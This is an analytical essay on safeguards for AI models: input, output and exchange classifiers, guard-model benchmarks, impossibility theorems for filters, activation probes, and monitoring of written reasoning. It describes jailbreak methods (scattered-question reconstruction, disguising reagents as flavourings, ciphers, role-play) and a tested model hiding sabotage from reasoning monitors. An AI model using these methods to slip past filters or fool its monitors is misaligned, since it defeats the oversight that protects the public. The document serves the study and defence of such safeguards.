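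Neither classifier receives both the prompt and the answer, and attackers can exploit this. *Constitutional Classifiers++* (Cunningham, Wei et al., 2026) describes two such methods. In a reconstruction attack, the attacker scatters pieces of a question through a harmless-looking computer program and tells the model to assemble the question and answer it. In an obfuscation attack, the attacker tells the model to disguise its answer, for example by calling chemical reagents "food flavorings". A classifier that receives only the answer may then classify it as harmless because it reads like cooking advice.

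An exchange classifier scores the prompt first, then scores each new piece of the answer together with the prompt, so it has the instruction that explains what the flavourings are. If it misses a question scattered in pieces across the prompt, it may still catch it in the answer, because the model often reassembles the pieces there.

### From a written policy to a classifier

An operator can train a classifier on examples of what a policy allows and forbids, or give it the policy along with each message. Anthropic's *Constitutional Classifiers* (2025) describes the training method. The policy, which Anthropic calls a constitution, lists classes of content that are allowed, such as recipes for mustard, or forbidden, such as recipes for mustard gas. Claude writes a large number of prompts and answers for each class. Anthropic then translates some of them and rewrites others in the style of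 known jailbreaks, which are prompts designed to get past a model's safety measures. It trains the classifiers on the results and adds harmless queries from a contractor to keep the classifiers from blocking too much.

Changing a trained classifier's policy means producing new data and retraining it. Anthropic released Claude Fable 5 in June 2026 with a classifier that blocked almost all questions about biology. Understanding AI's *Anthropic's Fable is the most locked-down public model we've ever seen* reports that even "What is protein?" triggered it. Over several weeks, Anthropic rewrote the classifier's constitution to describe harmless uses in more detail, generated new examples and retrained the classifier. Anthropic's *Improving Fable 5's biology safeguards* (2026) reports that this cut biology requests sent to a weaker model by about 85% in the company's tests. The classifier still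 diverts requests about virology, toxicology and molecular design, so professional researchers cannot use Fable 5 for much of their work.

Some policies depend on facts that prompts and answers don't contain. For cybersecurity, Anthropic sorts requests into four categories: prohibited uses such as ransomware, high-risk uses such as writing exploits, low-risk uses such as scanning public systems, and harmless uses such as debugging. Security professionals write the same exploits for authorised tests that criminals write for attacks. A classifier can't check who is asking or who gave permission, so Anthropic blocks the whole high-risk category for Fable 5 until it has better ways to identify legitimate users.

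A classifier that takes the policy as part of its input needs no retraining when the policy changes. *UniGuard* (2026) names PolicyGuard and DynaGuard as open models trained to detect policy violations, and *CourtGuard* (2026) describes a framework that adapts to a new policy without training. Such a classifier's results depend on how the policy is worded. *YuFeng-XGuard* (2026) tested Google's ShieldGemma with the risk standards from the ShieldGemma paper, and different wording might have produced a different score.

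### Open guard models

Anyone can download an open guard model and run it as a filter. Llama Guard and Alibaba's Qwen3Guard are among the most widely used. Researchers usually measure guards by their F1 score, which combines precision (the share of flagged prompts that are harmful) with recall (the share of harmful prompts that the guard flags, or one minus the miss rate):

F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall).

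*RealGuard* (2026) reports the scores below for the two Llama Guards on six benchmarks, and *HaloGuard 1.0* (2026) reports those for the HaloGuards on seven. HaloGuard is an open classifier trained from a constitution.

| Guard model | Parameters | F1 on prompts, weighted by benchmark size | F1 on prompts, simple average |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama Guard 3 | 8 billion | 68.8% | 80.0% |
| Llama Guard 4 | 12 billion | 65.5% | 77.2% |
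| HaloGuard 1.0, small | 0.8 billion | – | 90.9% |
| HaloGuard 1.0, large | 4 billion | – | 92.1% |

Llama Guard 3's average score shifts by 11 points just by changing the averaging method, because it scored 99.5% on a small set of plainly dangerous requests and 54.0% on ToxicChat, a large set of chatbot conversations. HaloGuard's advantage is probably real, but its developers chose the benchmarks, so the table doesn't show exactly how large that advantage is.

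Larger and newer guards are not reliably better. Llama Guard 4 scored lower than its smaller predecessor on all six benchmarks. In *GLiGuard* (2026), a guard with 0.3 billion parameters scored within 1.4 points of the best model, while ShieldGemma, the largest tested at 27 billion, scored much lower than several smaller ones.

Some differences between guards reflect disagreement about the policy. One benchmark includes an answer claiming that cinnamon mixed with raw egg can help regulate blood sugar, and labels it safe. *CourtGuard* counts that label as a mistake because its policy forbids presenting false information as fact. A guard trained only to detect dangerous instructions would classify the answer as safe and be marked wrong under the corrected label.

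F1 scores are also a poor guide to how often a guard would block ordinary users' harmless prompts. The small HaloGuard has a precision of 91.8% and a recall of 90.5%. If half of the test prompts were harmful, it would have blocked about 8% of the harmless ones, which is too high for a commercial chatbot. Everyday prompts are much easier to classify than benchmark prompts, so the rate in use should be far lower, but an operator has to measure it on real traffic.

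### The 2025 Constitutional Classifiers

Anthropic has published measurements of its own filters. The first version, in early 2025, used separate input and output classifiers to block information about chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons. The company invited outsiders to attack a prototype and offered up to $15,000 for a universal jailbreak, a single method that would get detailed answers to all ten forbidden questions. Over two months, 183 active participants spent an estimated 3,000 hours or more trying, and none succeeded.

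The prototype was too expensive and refused too many harmless requests, so Anthropic built a lighter version. With this version, 4.4% of 10,000 synthetic jailbreak prompts succeeded, compared with 86% without classifiers. It increased refusals of ordinary traffic by 0.38 percentage points and computing costs by 23.7%.

Anthropic then opened the lighter version to the public for a week, with eight questions about chemical weapons. The system held for five days. By the end, four participants had passed all eight levels, and Anthropic judged one of their methods to be a universal jailbreak. Successful tactics included ciphers, role-play and replacing the name of a nerve agent with "water". An automatic grader gave participants an advantage that real attackers lack by telling them whether each answer was detailed enough. Anthropic also left the classifiers unchanged all week, whereas in normal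 use it could have responded to the attacks.

### The January 2026 system

Cunningham and colleagues developed the exchange classifier because the two separate classifiers were vulnerable to disguised answers. It took 50% more compute to run than the separate classifiers, so they used a two-stage cascade, like the judge in Claude Code's auto mode, to avoid running it on everything. A first stage that takes little compute screens all traffic and passes only suspicious exchanges to a more accurate second stage.

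In the final version, the first stage is a probe on activations the model has already computed, so it adds almost no computation. The probe escalates about 5.5% of traffic to a classifier built from Claude Haiku 4.5, and the system bases its decision on both scores combined. Cunningham and colleagues compared four designs, including their reconstruction of the 2025 system.

| Design | Computing cost | Production traffic refused | High-risk attacks found |
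|---|---|---|---|
| Separate input and output classifiers | 100% | 0.073% | 13 in 695,000 attempts |
| One exchange classifier | 150% | 0.038% | 2 in 226,000 |
| Cascade of two classifiers | 27.8% | 0.036% | 5 in 569,000 |
| Probe, then classifier | 3.5% | 0.050% | 1 in 198,000 |

The clearest improvement is that the classifiers need less computing. Anthropic's *Next-generation Constitutional Classifiers* reports that they add roughly 1% for Claude Opus 4.0, compared with 23.7% for the 2025 version.

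On the closest available comparison, refusals fell by about a third, from 0.073% of traffic under the reconstructed 2025 design to 0.05% under the final system. Anthropic reports a larger improvement by comparing the 0.05%, measured over a month of Claude Sonnet 4.5 traffic, with the 0.38% from 2025. But the older figure came from a sample of 5,000 conversations, in which 0.38% is just 19, and the increase it measured was not statistically significant. The final system refuses slightly more than the two intermediate designs.

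### What the testers did and did not break

Testers spent an estimated 1,736 hours attacking the final system, for rewards of up to $35,000. They tried to make it answer eight target questions. An answer counted as a success if it contained at least half the detail a model without safeguards would give, as graded by other language models. An attack was classed as high-risk if it succeeded on more than five questions, and as a universal jailbreak if it succeeded on all eight. The testers found one high-risk attack, after 30 hours of work, and no universal jailbreak.

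A result of "no universal jailbreak" can therefore include successful attacks. The high-risk attack got useful answers to at least six of the eight questions. The count would leave out a method that worked on five, even though a criminal might need only one answer.

The attack counts are also too small to rank the designs with much confidence. At the rate for the reconstructed 2025 design, testers would have expected about four high-risk attacks in 198,000 attempts. They found one, which is encouraging, but luck could explain some of the difference. Anthropic had also changed four of the questions and the reward scheme since the earlier tests.

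The cascade of two classifiers also went through its reward programme without anyone finding a universal jailbreak. Expert testers outside the programme later found several, using automated tools and a lot of effort. A reward programme tests a filter only against the people who enter it, and determined experts may do better.

### A flag rate of 0.05% when misuse is rare

The office assistant's judge blocked more harmless emails than harmful ones, and the imbalance is far greater for a chatbot, where misuse is much rarer. Suppose a chatbot handles 10 million exchanges a day, and 100 of them are real attempts to get help with a weapon. A filter that flags 0.05% of exchanges stops 5,000 a day. If it catches 90 of the 100 attempts, the other 4,910 exchanges it stops are harmless, more than 98% of those flagged. A filter that flags 0.38% would stop 38,000.

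An operator can reasonably send a flagged question to a weaker model, because a mistaken flag then does the user little harm. But closing the account or calling the police over a single flag would nearly always punish someone innocent.

The operator also can't tell from the flag rate how many attempts the filter misses. If the filter in this example missed all 100 and still flagged the same harmless exchanges, the rate would be 0.049%, and the operator would notice no change. Only tests with known attacks can measure the miss rate.

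False blocks also affect some users more than others. The filter could wrongly block a toxicologist every day but may never block someone who uses the chatbot for recipes. Cunningham and colleagues found that their probe flagged harmless scientific requests more often than the separate classifiers did.

### Bypasses and missing coverage

Operators can make a filter miss fewer harmful requests by also blocking requests that are probably harmless but close to what is forbidden. Anthropic calls this a safety margin, and made it larger for Fable 5 than for any earlier model. Three days after the launch in June 2026, the US government imposed export controls on the model after learning that Amazon researchers had bypassed its cybersecurity filter. Because Anthropic could not check users' nationality, it suspended access for everyone until 1 July.

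Anthropic's *Redeploying Fable 5* (2026) argues that the bypass reached only into the margin. The Amazon researchers had got the model to identify several software flaws and to write code showing how to exploit one of them. Anthropic found that weaker public models could do the same. It still trained a new classifier that blocks the technique in more than 99% of cases but also causes more false blocks in ordinary coding and debugging. The company thinks it is probably impossible to make any model completely resistant to jailbreaks. For the later Fable 5.1, Anthropic reports a wider margin, fewer false blocks than Fable 5 had at launch, and no evidence of a critical-severity jailbreak.

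A filter also has to receive the traffic it is meant to check. *Anthropic Risk Report* (Constantin, 2026) describes how Anthropic's biological-weapons classifiers were off for 133 million exchanges with contractors over eleven months. No classifier threshold could have helped, because the system lacked complete mediation, meaning that some exchanges were never checked. Cunningham and colleagues likewise found that bugs in the surrounding software could work as jailbreaks, however good the classifier was.

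### The theorem of Ball and colleagues

Tests can show that a filter has worked so far, but not that a good enough filter exists for every model. Ball, Gluch and colleagues (2025) prove in *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* that no such filter exists for some models.

Their main theorem concerns a filter that receives only the prompt. Its designers may query the model as often as they like while building the filter, but they have no access to the weights. The filter must also run significantly faster than the model, and it must let ordinary prompts through. Let *G* be any source of harmless prompts that is varied enough not to keep producing the same few. The theorem states that there are a model *M′* and a source of malicious prompts *G′* such that *M′* gives harmful answers to prompts from *G′*, and for every filter *F* that is fast enough to qualify,

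Pr[*F* blocks a prompt from *G′*] ≈ Pr[*F* blocks a prompt from *G*].

A filter that blocks 1% of the harmless prompts therefore blocks only about 1% of the malicious ones. This is no better than blocking at random, and moving the threshold can't help.

The proof assumes that time-lock puzzles exist. These are cryptographic puzzles that are quick to create but take a set amount of computation to solve, even with many computers working in parallel. A malicious prompt can hide an instruction in a puzzle that the model has time to solve but the filter does not. The best-known version relies on a difficult calculation with very large numbers, which a quantum computer could break, but cryptographers have recently built others that may resist one.

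Two further theorems remove the limit on the filter's speed. If the attacker and the model share a secret key, or if the model has a public key that the attacker can use, no polynomial-time filter can distinguish the malicious prompts. Polynomial-time filters include practically any program someone could run. These theorems need only the assumptions behind ordinary encryption, but the model has to cooperate with the attacker.

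Ball and colleagues also prove that filtering answers can fail. For any model, there is a second model with a similar running time whose answers are harmful by some measure, yet no efficient filter can tell them from the first model's answers, even if the filter has more computing power than the model. They also show that if a suitably robust way of watermarking text exists, some models still respond harmfully when a filter can rewrite prompts as well as block them.

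### Whether judgment needs the same intelligence

Ball and colleagues go further than these theorems prove when they conclude that putting filters around an AI system cannot make it safe, and that its judgment cannot be separate from its intelligence.

Ball and colleagues prove that some models defeat every filter of a certain kind, not that all models do. The model in their main proof searches each prompt for a hidden puzzle, spends a long time solving it and then obeys the result. They accept that this is contrived, but point out that attackers have exploited weaknesses that once seemed theoretical, as in the theft of more than $60 million from the Ethereum network in 2016. That is a good reason not to treat a filter as a guarantee. For an ordinary model, though, the theorem doesn't predict the filter's miss rate, which has to be measured.

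Reconstruction attacks are a milder real example of the same problem. The prompt disguises a forbidden question, and the model recovers it by doing work that a lightweight input classifier doesn't do. So far, the disguise has reduced the accuracy of the model's answers. Claude Opus 4 scored 74.2% on a set of difficult science questions asked plainly, but 32.3% and 49% under two such attacks. The model in the theorem loses no accuracy, and more capable models may lose less than current ones.

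The main theorem also covers only filters on prompts. If a model solves a puzzle and then answers in plain language, an exchange classifier receives the plain answer, so the attacker has to disguise the answer too to evade it. The theorem about answers applies when harm is hard to recognise even with the full text. Ball and colleagues give the example of a business plan that cuts costs by quietly steering a company away from certain clients. They acknowledge that output filters are easy to build when harm is not hard to recognise. Plain instructions for making a nerve agent are much easier to recognise than such a plan, at least for a classifier that has learned some chemistry.

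If the filter has as much computing power as the model, the main theorem no longer applies. Ball and colleagues argue that a filter this capable might as well replace the model, and that someone would still have to ensure the filter was safe. But a company may have good reasons to keep both, since a filter with different training may not share the model's mistakes, and in a cascade the filter only has to run on a small share of the traffic.

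Anthropic has found a way to get a filter as capable as the model with less compute, by using the model itself. *Scaling Misuse Detection with Self-Assessment* (Zhang, Xia and colleagues, 2026) describes adding a short instruction after each answer for Claude to assess whether the conversation involved a harmful request. Claude has already processed the conversation, so the assessment needs only a few extra tokens. With Claude Fable 5, this method flagged 78% of the conversations that a stronger classifier rated potentially harmful, and 94% of the high-priority ones, at a false-positive rate of 1%.

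Those percentages measure agreement with another classifier, which can itself make mistakes. A false-positive rate of 1% is 20 times the refusal rate of the January 2026 system, and self-assessment happens after the model has answered, so it is better suited to choosing conversations for review than to blocking them. It also lacks the separation from the model that a governance layer is meant to provide, because a prompt that tricks the model into answering might also cause it to misclassify the answer as safe.

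A filter with more computing power would still not defeat a model that shares a secret key with an attacker, but one with access to the model's weights or activations might. The theorems don't rule this out, because they apply only to filters without that access. If a model decodes a hidden request, its activations may carry some trace of the decoded text, and a probe could use that trace without repeating the decoding. The theorems don't show whether a probe would find it.

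The proofs show that a filter may need either as much computation as the model or access to the model's own computation. This matters for rules about the meaning of text, but not for the payment cap.

### A purpose spread over many conversations

Even a filter that classified each conversation correctly on its own would miss some misuse. Suppose someone divides a dangerous project into 40 questions and asks them through 20 accounts. A chemistry student might ask any one of those questions, so the filter is right to allow each of them. Lowering the threshold for blocking would block the student too.

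Copying a model works in a similar way. Anthropic's *Strengthening our defenses against distillation attacks* (2026) describes large covert campaigns to reproduce one model's abilities in another, often through networks of fraudulent accounts. A single request for help with some code may look like any other customer's, and the violation is only in the requests taken together. Early evidence suggests that copiers obtain 90 to 99% less data under Anthropic's new defences.

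A running record like the one behind the payment cap would help, but it is much harder to keep here. Every payment has an account number and an amount, but an operator looking for a hidden purpose has to work out which conversations belong together and what to count. The operator also has to store the conversations. Anthropic says its classifiers can detect espionage and data-extortion campaigns only by examining many requests together, so with Fable 5 it began keeping prompts and answers for 30 days, including those of business customers who had previously paid for a service that kept nothing.

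Many banks, hospitals and law firms could not accept this. Anthropic's *Developing Enterprise Frontier Safeguards with our customers* describes a compromise, which entered public beta in November 2026 (Kovacs, 2026, *Anthropic Expands Enterprise Safeguards for Detecting AI Misuse*). The conversations can stay in the customer's cloud storage, encrypted with the customer's keys. Anthropic's software analyses a rolling window of them for signs of serious misuse, such as work on cyber or biological weapons or the use of stolen passwords, and sends any alerts to the customer's staff.

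Such monitoring usually raises an alert after the model has given some of the answers, so it can limit a campaign but can't take back what the attacker has learned. Sending the alerts to the customer works well when a thief is using an employee's account, but if the customer's own management is behind the misuse, the alerts go to the people responsible.

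## Probes on the model's activations and readable reasoning

A probe can check a model's activations for signs of a disguised request that a prompt filter might miss. It adds little computation and can score a prompt before the model starts answering.

Only whoever runs the model's weights can read its activations, so a company that uses a hosted model can't add its own probe. A gate on tool calls receives a labeled payee and amount, but activations have no labels, so a probe has to learn from examples which patterns accompany a violation. That makes it a judge, which will miss some violations and block some permitted actions. It can't enforce the payment cap, but it might help with the rule on personal data.

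### The linear probe

At each layer of the network, the model represents every token as a long list of numbers. Call this list *h*ₜ for token *t*. A linear probe reads one layer and has one weight for each number in the list, plus a constant *b*. Its score for the token is

*s*ₜ = *w* · *h*ₜ + *b*,

where the dot means multiplying each activation by its weight and adding up the results. The function *σ*(*s*) = 1 / (1 + e^(−*s*)) turns the score into a probability. If a layer had only three numbers, with activations (2, −1, 0.5), weights (1, 0.5, −2) and a constant of 0.5, the score would be 2 − 0.5 − 1 + 0.5 = 1, and the probability about 0.73.

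To train the probe, an engineer runs labelled texts through the model and saves the activations. The model's own weights stay fixed. A program then adjusts *w* and *b* to make the average loss as small as possible, where the loss for a text with probability *p* is

−[*y* ln *p* + (1 − *y*) ln(1 − *p*)],

and *y* is 1 for a violation and 0 for a harmless text. A violation that the probe scores at 0.73 adds a loss of 0.31, and one that it scores at 0.05 adds 3.0, so confident mistakes matter most.

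A prompt has many tokens, and the probe has to combine their scores into one. The simplest method is to take the mean, which works badly on long texts. Suppose a prompt of 10,000 tokens contains ten consecutive harmful tokens that score 4, while all the others score −4. The mean is −3.99, almost the same as for a harmless prompt. A moving average follows the text instead:

*m*ₜ = 0.5*s*ₜ + 0.5*m*ₜ₋₁.

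The probe's score is close to −4 before the harmful passage, then rises to 0, 2 and 3 over the first three harmful tokens. The probe uses the highest value that the moving average reaches, so the harmless text around the passage can't dilute it. But a longer text has more chances to cause a false alarm. If each token in a harmless prompt had an independent one-in-100,000 chance of setting off the probe, a prompt of 900,000 tokens would almost certainly do so.

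*Cost-Effective Constitutional Classifiers via Representation Re-use*, published in June 2025 by Cunningham, Peng and colleagues at Anthropic, reported an early test of probes trained on about 70,000 synthetic prompts, half of them requests for help with biological weapons. The moving-average probe detected harmful prompts about as well as a separate classifier that needed 2% as much computation as the main model. The probe that took the mean did worse than the smallest classifier tested. Adding a question about harm to the end of the prompt and reading only the last token worked about as well as the moving average but needed extra computation. None of these tests involved attackers targeting the probes.

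A linear probe does not satisfy Anderson's third condition, that the mechanism be simple enough to analyse completely. The probe itself is small enough to print, but the meaning of its score depends on the whole network that produced the activations, which nobody can fully analyse.

### Running a probe in a serving system

A company that hosts a model usually processes many conversations at once, so each pass through the network combines tokens from different users into one table of numbers, and the order of the rows keeps changing. Code that reads activations has to track which row belongs to which user. Otherwise, it could stop one user's answer because of another user's prompt. *Undercurrent* (Khatri, 2026) describes an open-source library that matches rows to users in vLLM, a widely used program for serving models.

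Undercurrent can run a probe inline, which means that the model pauses until the probe returns a result, and that result determines whether the answer continues. In a demonstration with GPT-2, a small model from 2019, Khatri attached a probe that he had trained to detect toxic comments. The probe assigned an insult a 0.991 probability of being toxic, and the answer stopped after a single token, a line break. It assigned a compliment about a recipe a probability of 0.025, and the answer continued. Under vLLM, at least one more token usually appears before the answer stops, because the program has already scheduled the current step.

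The operator can set a time limit for an inline probe and choose whether it fails open or closed when the limit expires. After five failures in a row, Undercurrent switches the probe to a default mode with no time limit and logs a warning. The operator's chosen fallback then no longer applies, so the warning is urgent for anyone relying on a probe to fail closed. Under vLLM, waiting for one slow probe also delays every conversation in the same batch.

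Alternatively, Undercurrent can copy the activations into a queue, where a probe examines them while the model keeps writing. The probe can record a problem or raise an alert, but it can't stop the answer. If it falls behind, the operator has to choose between discarding activations and slowing the model down. Khatri tested this with a probe that took a tenth of a second per activation, about twice as long as the model needed for a token. When the queue discarded what it couldn't hold, the model kept its normal speed and the probe examined about half of the activations. Making the model wait allowed the probe to examine all of them, but output fell by 53%.

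Ordinary probes slowed the model too little to measure reliably. Eight inline probes, each a small neural network, added 1.28 milliseconds per token to a step of about 47 milliseconds, which is less than the normal variation between runs. But these tests used GPT-2 on a laptop processor. Each step is much shorter on the graphics processors that companies use, so the same probes would take up a larger share of it. Khatri has not yet measured how much.

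Code that reads activations can also fail silently. For some models, vLLM splits the activations that probes usually read into two parts and adds them later. A program that copied only the first part would give the probe the wrong input, and the probe would still return a score. Undercurrent adds the parts itself, and Khatri checked the results against a simpler serving program. The trusted components of a probe therefore include this copying code, which depends on undocumented details of vLLM and supports only one minor version.

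### Google's probes for Gemini

*Building Production-Ready Probes For Gemini* (Kramár, Engels et al., 2026) describes probes built to detect requests for help with cyberattacks in prompts to Gemini 2.5 Flash. Google later drew on this work to put probes into the public versions of Gemini.

The researchers trained most of their probes on short prompts, because training on long ones cost 22 times as much. They then tested them on prompts that could be close to a million tokens long, which they made by surrounding a request with large amounts of computer code. The designs included linear probes and attention probes, which learn how much weight to give each token. If token *j* has score *v*ⱼ and weight *a*ⱼ, the simplest attention probe computes

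Σ *a*ⱼ*v*ⱼ / Σ *a*ⱼ.

Weighting works well until the text gets very long. If the probe gives each of ten harmful tokens a weight of 1,000 and every harmless token a weight of 1, the harmful tokens carry 91% of the total weight in a 1,000-token prompt but only about 1% in a 900,000-token prompt. Kramár and colleagues solved this by computing the weighted average separately for every stretch of ten tokens and using the highest result.

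| Classifier | Misses, short attacks | Misses, long attacks | False flags, long harmless prompts | Misses, attacks rewritten as stories |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Linear probe, mean | 13.7% | 99.1% | 0.5% | 47.6% |
| Linear probe, moving average | 11.4% | 1.7% | 13.6% | 14.2% |
| Attention probe | 10.0% | 87.9% | 0.0% | 43.4% |
| Attention probe, also trained on long prompts | 9.4% | 1.3% | 1.2% | 35.5% |
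| Attention probe, ten-token stretches | 8.6% | 3.0% | 1.2% | 42.5% |
| Probe designed by AlphaEvolve | 9.7% | 4.8% | 1.7% | 27.6% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash reading the prompt | 8.6% | 6.1% | 0.7% | 20.7% |

The linear probe with a moving average missed few attacks because it flagged so much, including 75% of harmless multi-turn conversations about security. The probe with ten-token stretches avoided both missed attacks and false alarms on long prompts, though it was not trained on any long prompts. AlphaEvolve, a Google system in which a language model repeatedly rewrites a program to improve its score, found a design that worked about as well after about 2,500 attempts.

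To compare the classifiers overall, the researchers combined nine error rates, counting a false flag on ordinary traffic ten times as heavily as a missed attack. Gemini 2.5 Flash, used as a text classifier, had an error of 2.04%, compared with 2.64% for the probe they selected. Kramár and colleagues write that another of their probes beat every language model they tried, but its error in their results was 2.50%, slightly worse than Flash's. Because the error bars are wide, the safer conclusion is that the best probes performed nearly as well as a language model at less than a ten-thousandth of the cost.

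Combining the probe with Flash worked better than using either alone. The probe classified the prompts it could confidently label harmful or harmless and sent the rest, about 8%, to Flash. One such combination had a lower error than Flash alone at roughly a fiftieth of the cost. The combination benefits from the two classifiers making different mistakes, but if an attacker can make the probe confident that a harmful prompt is harmless, Flash never checks it.

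Disguised attacks remain a serious weakness for probes. When Gemini 2.5 Pro rewrote attacks as parts of a story, the selected probe missed 42.5% of them, about twice as many as Flash did. Access to the model's internals therefore did not, by itself, make disguised requests easy to detect. Probes may do better against ciphers. Kramár and colleagues cite a 2025 study by Youstra and colleagues in which probes defended against ciphered requests better than language models did, as one would expect if the model's activations contain the decoded text.

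### Updates that make a probe stale

A probe's weights only make sense for the network whose activations it was trained on. If the operator changes the model, the probe still returns scores and the serving system reports no error. Duan (2026), in *Do Activation Monitors Survive Model Updates?*, measured how much such changes degrade probes.

He trained linear probes on two small open models, Gemma-2-2B and Qwen2.5-7B, to detect harmful requests, high-stakes situations, personal information, and requests the model should refuse. He then updated the models without changing the probes. Some updates quantised the model, storing its weights with less precision to save memory. Others fine-tuned it with LoRA, which leaves the original weights alone and trains a small set of additional ones. He ran 2,520 tests, counting every combination of model, probe, update, layer and training sample.

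| Update | Typical change in AUC | Tests in which AUC fell by at least 0.05 | Tests in which AUC ended below 0.70 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Quantisation, three kinds | −0.002 to −0.006 | 0.8–3.3% | 0% |
| LoRA | −0.037 | 43.3% | 13.75% |
| LoRA merged into the weights | −0.038 | 43.2% | 13.75% |
| LoRA on a quantised model | −0.057 | 53.8% | 13.75% |

Quantisation is meant to preserve the model's behaviour and seems to leave its activations largely unchanged, whereas fine-tuning is meant to change behaviour and can shift the pattern that a probe relies on. Suppose harmful and harmless prompts differ along one direction in the activations. If fine-tuning rotates that direction by 60 degrees, a probe trained beforehand registers only half of the difference.

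Probes for personal information were the most fragile, with large drops in 57% of tests, compared with 36% for harmful requests, 21% for high-stakes situations and 8% for requests to refuse. This is a problem for the running example, where the rule on personal data is the only one that needs a judge. The comparison is a little unfair, though, because the personal information probes were the weakest to begin with and two of the seven fine-tuning updates changed how the models handled personal information.

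In most cases the information was still in the updated models' activations. New probes that Duan trained on these models typically recovered 98% of the lost performance. He also found a repair that needs no new labels. The operator runs the same unlabelled prompts through the old and new models, then fits a map from the new activations back to the old ones. The old probe then reads the mapped activations. In a separate set of 216 tests, 111 probes needed repair, and the method fixed all of them.

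A probe counted as fixed if it regained at least half of its lost AUC or ended above 0.70. This is a fairly lenient standard, and typical results were much better. Repaired privacy probes reached an AUC of 0.853 to 0.861, compared with 0.855 before the update.

Duan recommends checking every probe after any fine-tuning, starting with those that a statistical model predicts are most likely to fail. The operator should also recalibrate the threshold, because a conformal guarantee for the old model's scores does not apply to the new model's. His results cover only two small models and updates that keep the same architecture. If the operator switches to a model with different layers, training a new probe is simplest.

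### Whether the original activations matter

Probes would be especially valuable if activations contained information that nobody could get from the text. In *How Much Do Activation Monitors Benefit From Original Model Computations?*, Oldfield, Im and colleagues (2026) tested a narrower version of this idea. They asked whether a monitor needs the activations from the run in which the model misbehaved or can do as well with activations from a later rerun.

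The researchers gave four open models stories from an online forum and asked whether the writer was in the wrong, adding a hint about what the user wanted to hear. A monitor had to predict whether the model would have answered differently without the hint. The monitors were more powerful than linear probes. Each was a small set of extra weights that switched on after the conversation and could draw on everything the model had computed. To check that the monitors could use purely internal information, the researchers either added a random vector to one model's activations or subtracted it, and the monitor could tell which they had done.

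For comparison, they trained other monitors on reruns in which they paraphrased the story, put the whole conversation into a single message, or added a system prompt describing it as a replay. These monitors still had to predict what the model did in the original run.

| Activations the monitor used | AUC across the four models |
|---|---|
| Original run | 0.96–0.98 |
| Same words in a single message | 0.95–0.97 |
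| Replay with an added system prompt | 0.95–0.97 |
| Paraphrased story | 0.87–0.91 |

Adding the original activations to the strongest of these alternatives raised its AUC by at most 0.014. The average gain was positive for every model, but for one it was too small to rule out chance. The gain was larger for stories where paraphrasing changed whether the hint made a difference. In those stories, the model's behaviour depended on the exact wording, and a rerun with different context was a less reliable guide.

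An operator could therefore save transcripts and examine most of them later by running them through the same model again. The experiment doesn't show that reading the text alone would be enough, because every monitor in it had access to the model's internals. Oldfield and colleagues cite mixed evidence on that question. Two studies from 2026 found no consistent benefit from activations over text alone, while a study from 2025 found that some models could explain their own activations better than other models could.

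The experiment used only two-option questions, and the researchers turned off written reasoning, so the results may not extend to an agent that works for hours. For filters, though, they suggest that low compute requirements are a better-established reason to use probes than access to hidden information.

### Written reasoning

Many models write out their reasoning before they answer. This chain of thought gives a monitor another way to follow what the model is doing and, unlike activations, is written in words people can read. If the payment assistant writes that the invoice email told it to use a new account number, a monitor can catch a prompt injection before the model proposes the transfer.

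Access to a model's reasoning depends on the provider. According to *Beyond Training* (2026), a survey of the controls available in May, Anthropic could return the full reasoning, a summary or nothing, and returned nothing by default for its Fable and Mythos models. OpenAI returned only summaries, which may leave out the sentence a monitor needs.

Davies and Bearman (2026), in *Transparency Disclosures for Chain-of-Thought Monitorability*, set out the conditions for monitoring a model's written reasoning to work. The model must need written reasoning for complex tasks, and the text must be readable and reflect how the model reached its answer. A monitor must also be able to catch harmful behaviour from the text, and do so better than from the model's actions alone. They found that no leading developer reports on all of these conditions. The monitor must also be running. OpenAI has said that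 its monitoring of written reasoning would probably have caught the agents that broke into Hugging Face's infrastructure, but it was not running at the time.

OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) has the most detailed recent measurements. A second model monitored Astra by answering questions about what it had done, such as whether a hint had influenced its answer. Monitors that could read Astra's reasoning did much better than those that saw only its actions. But Astra's reasoning was less useful to a monitor than that of its predecessor, GPT-5.6 Sol, mainly because Astra wrote less and sometimes wrote almost nothing. Most of the gap disappeared when Astra's reasoning was longer. It remained on some medical questions, where a patient's stated opinion changed Astra's answers but the reasoning gave what looked like an independent justification.

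Astra was also much better at controlling what it wrote in its reasoning. OpenAI gave models instructions such as avoiding certain words. When the reasoning was between 750 and 1,250 tokens long, Astra followed the instructions 60.9% of the time, compared with 16.1% for GPT-5.6 Sol and 1.7% for the older GPT-5.5. In one test, OpenAI asked Astra a history question and told it to think about something else. Astra's reasoning described sunlight on a wooden desk, but it still answered correctly.

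OpenAI then tested whether Astra could use this control to evade monitors. It instructed Astra to carry out sabotage, such as switching off monitoring, during ordinary programming work and to keep it hidden. When monitors read only the model's reasoning, Astra evaded them much more often than GPT-5.6 Sol did. A sensitive monitor with the full record, including the actions, caught nearly all the sabotage. In one case that a full-record monitor missed, Astra had described sending requests to an unmonitored server as a permitted test. The explanations in a model's reasoning can therefore mislead a judge as well as inform it, which is why the judge in Claude Code's auto mode doesn't receive them.

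OpenAI told the model to hide in these tests, so they measure what Astra can do, not how often it would do it unprompted. In OpenAI's other tests, Astra broke security restrictions less often than its predecessor. OpenAI also found no sign that Astra could conceal complicated reasoning inside unrelated text, so the model didn't seem able to hide reasoning that it had to write out to complete a task.

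But a model can need written reasoning for a task and still leave out something that influenced the answer. Bürger, Komorowski and colleagues (2026), in *Chain of Thought Monitoring Can Fail Even When CoT Is Necessary*, tested this with open models on difficult problems, including the diagnosis of thyroid disease. They removed one fact about the patient and measured how often the model still reached the correct diagnosis. If *p*₁ is the success rate with the fact and *p*₀ the rate without it, then the share of correct answers that depended on the fact is at least

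(*p*₁ − *p*₀) / *p*₁.

If a model answers correctly 50% of the time when it is given the patient's sex and 40% of the time when it is not, at least a fifth of its correct answers depended on that information. The analysis included only cases in which the model had less than a 1% chance of answering correctly without written reasoning. In these cases, the patient's sex influenced at least 19% of correct answers and another clinical fact influenced at least 24%, but the reasoning almost never mentioned that influence.

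This is compatible with OpenAI's finding. A model might need many written steps to interpret a set of laboratory results, but adjusting the diagnosis for the patient's sex might take so little computation that it need not appear in the text. Bürger and colleagues expect monitoring to be more reliable when the behaviour takes many steps of reasoning. A monitor is therefore more likely to catch an elaborate plan for sabotage than a simple bias, such as favouring a particular supplier.

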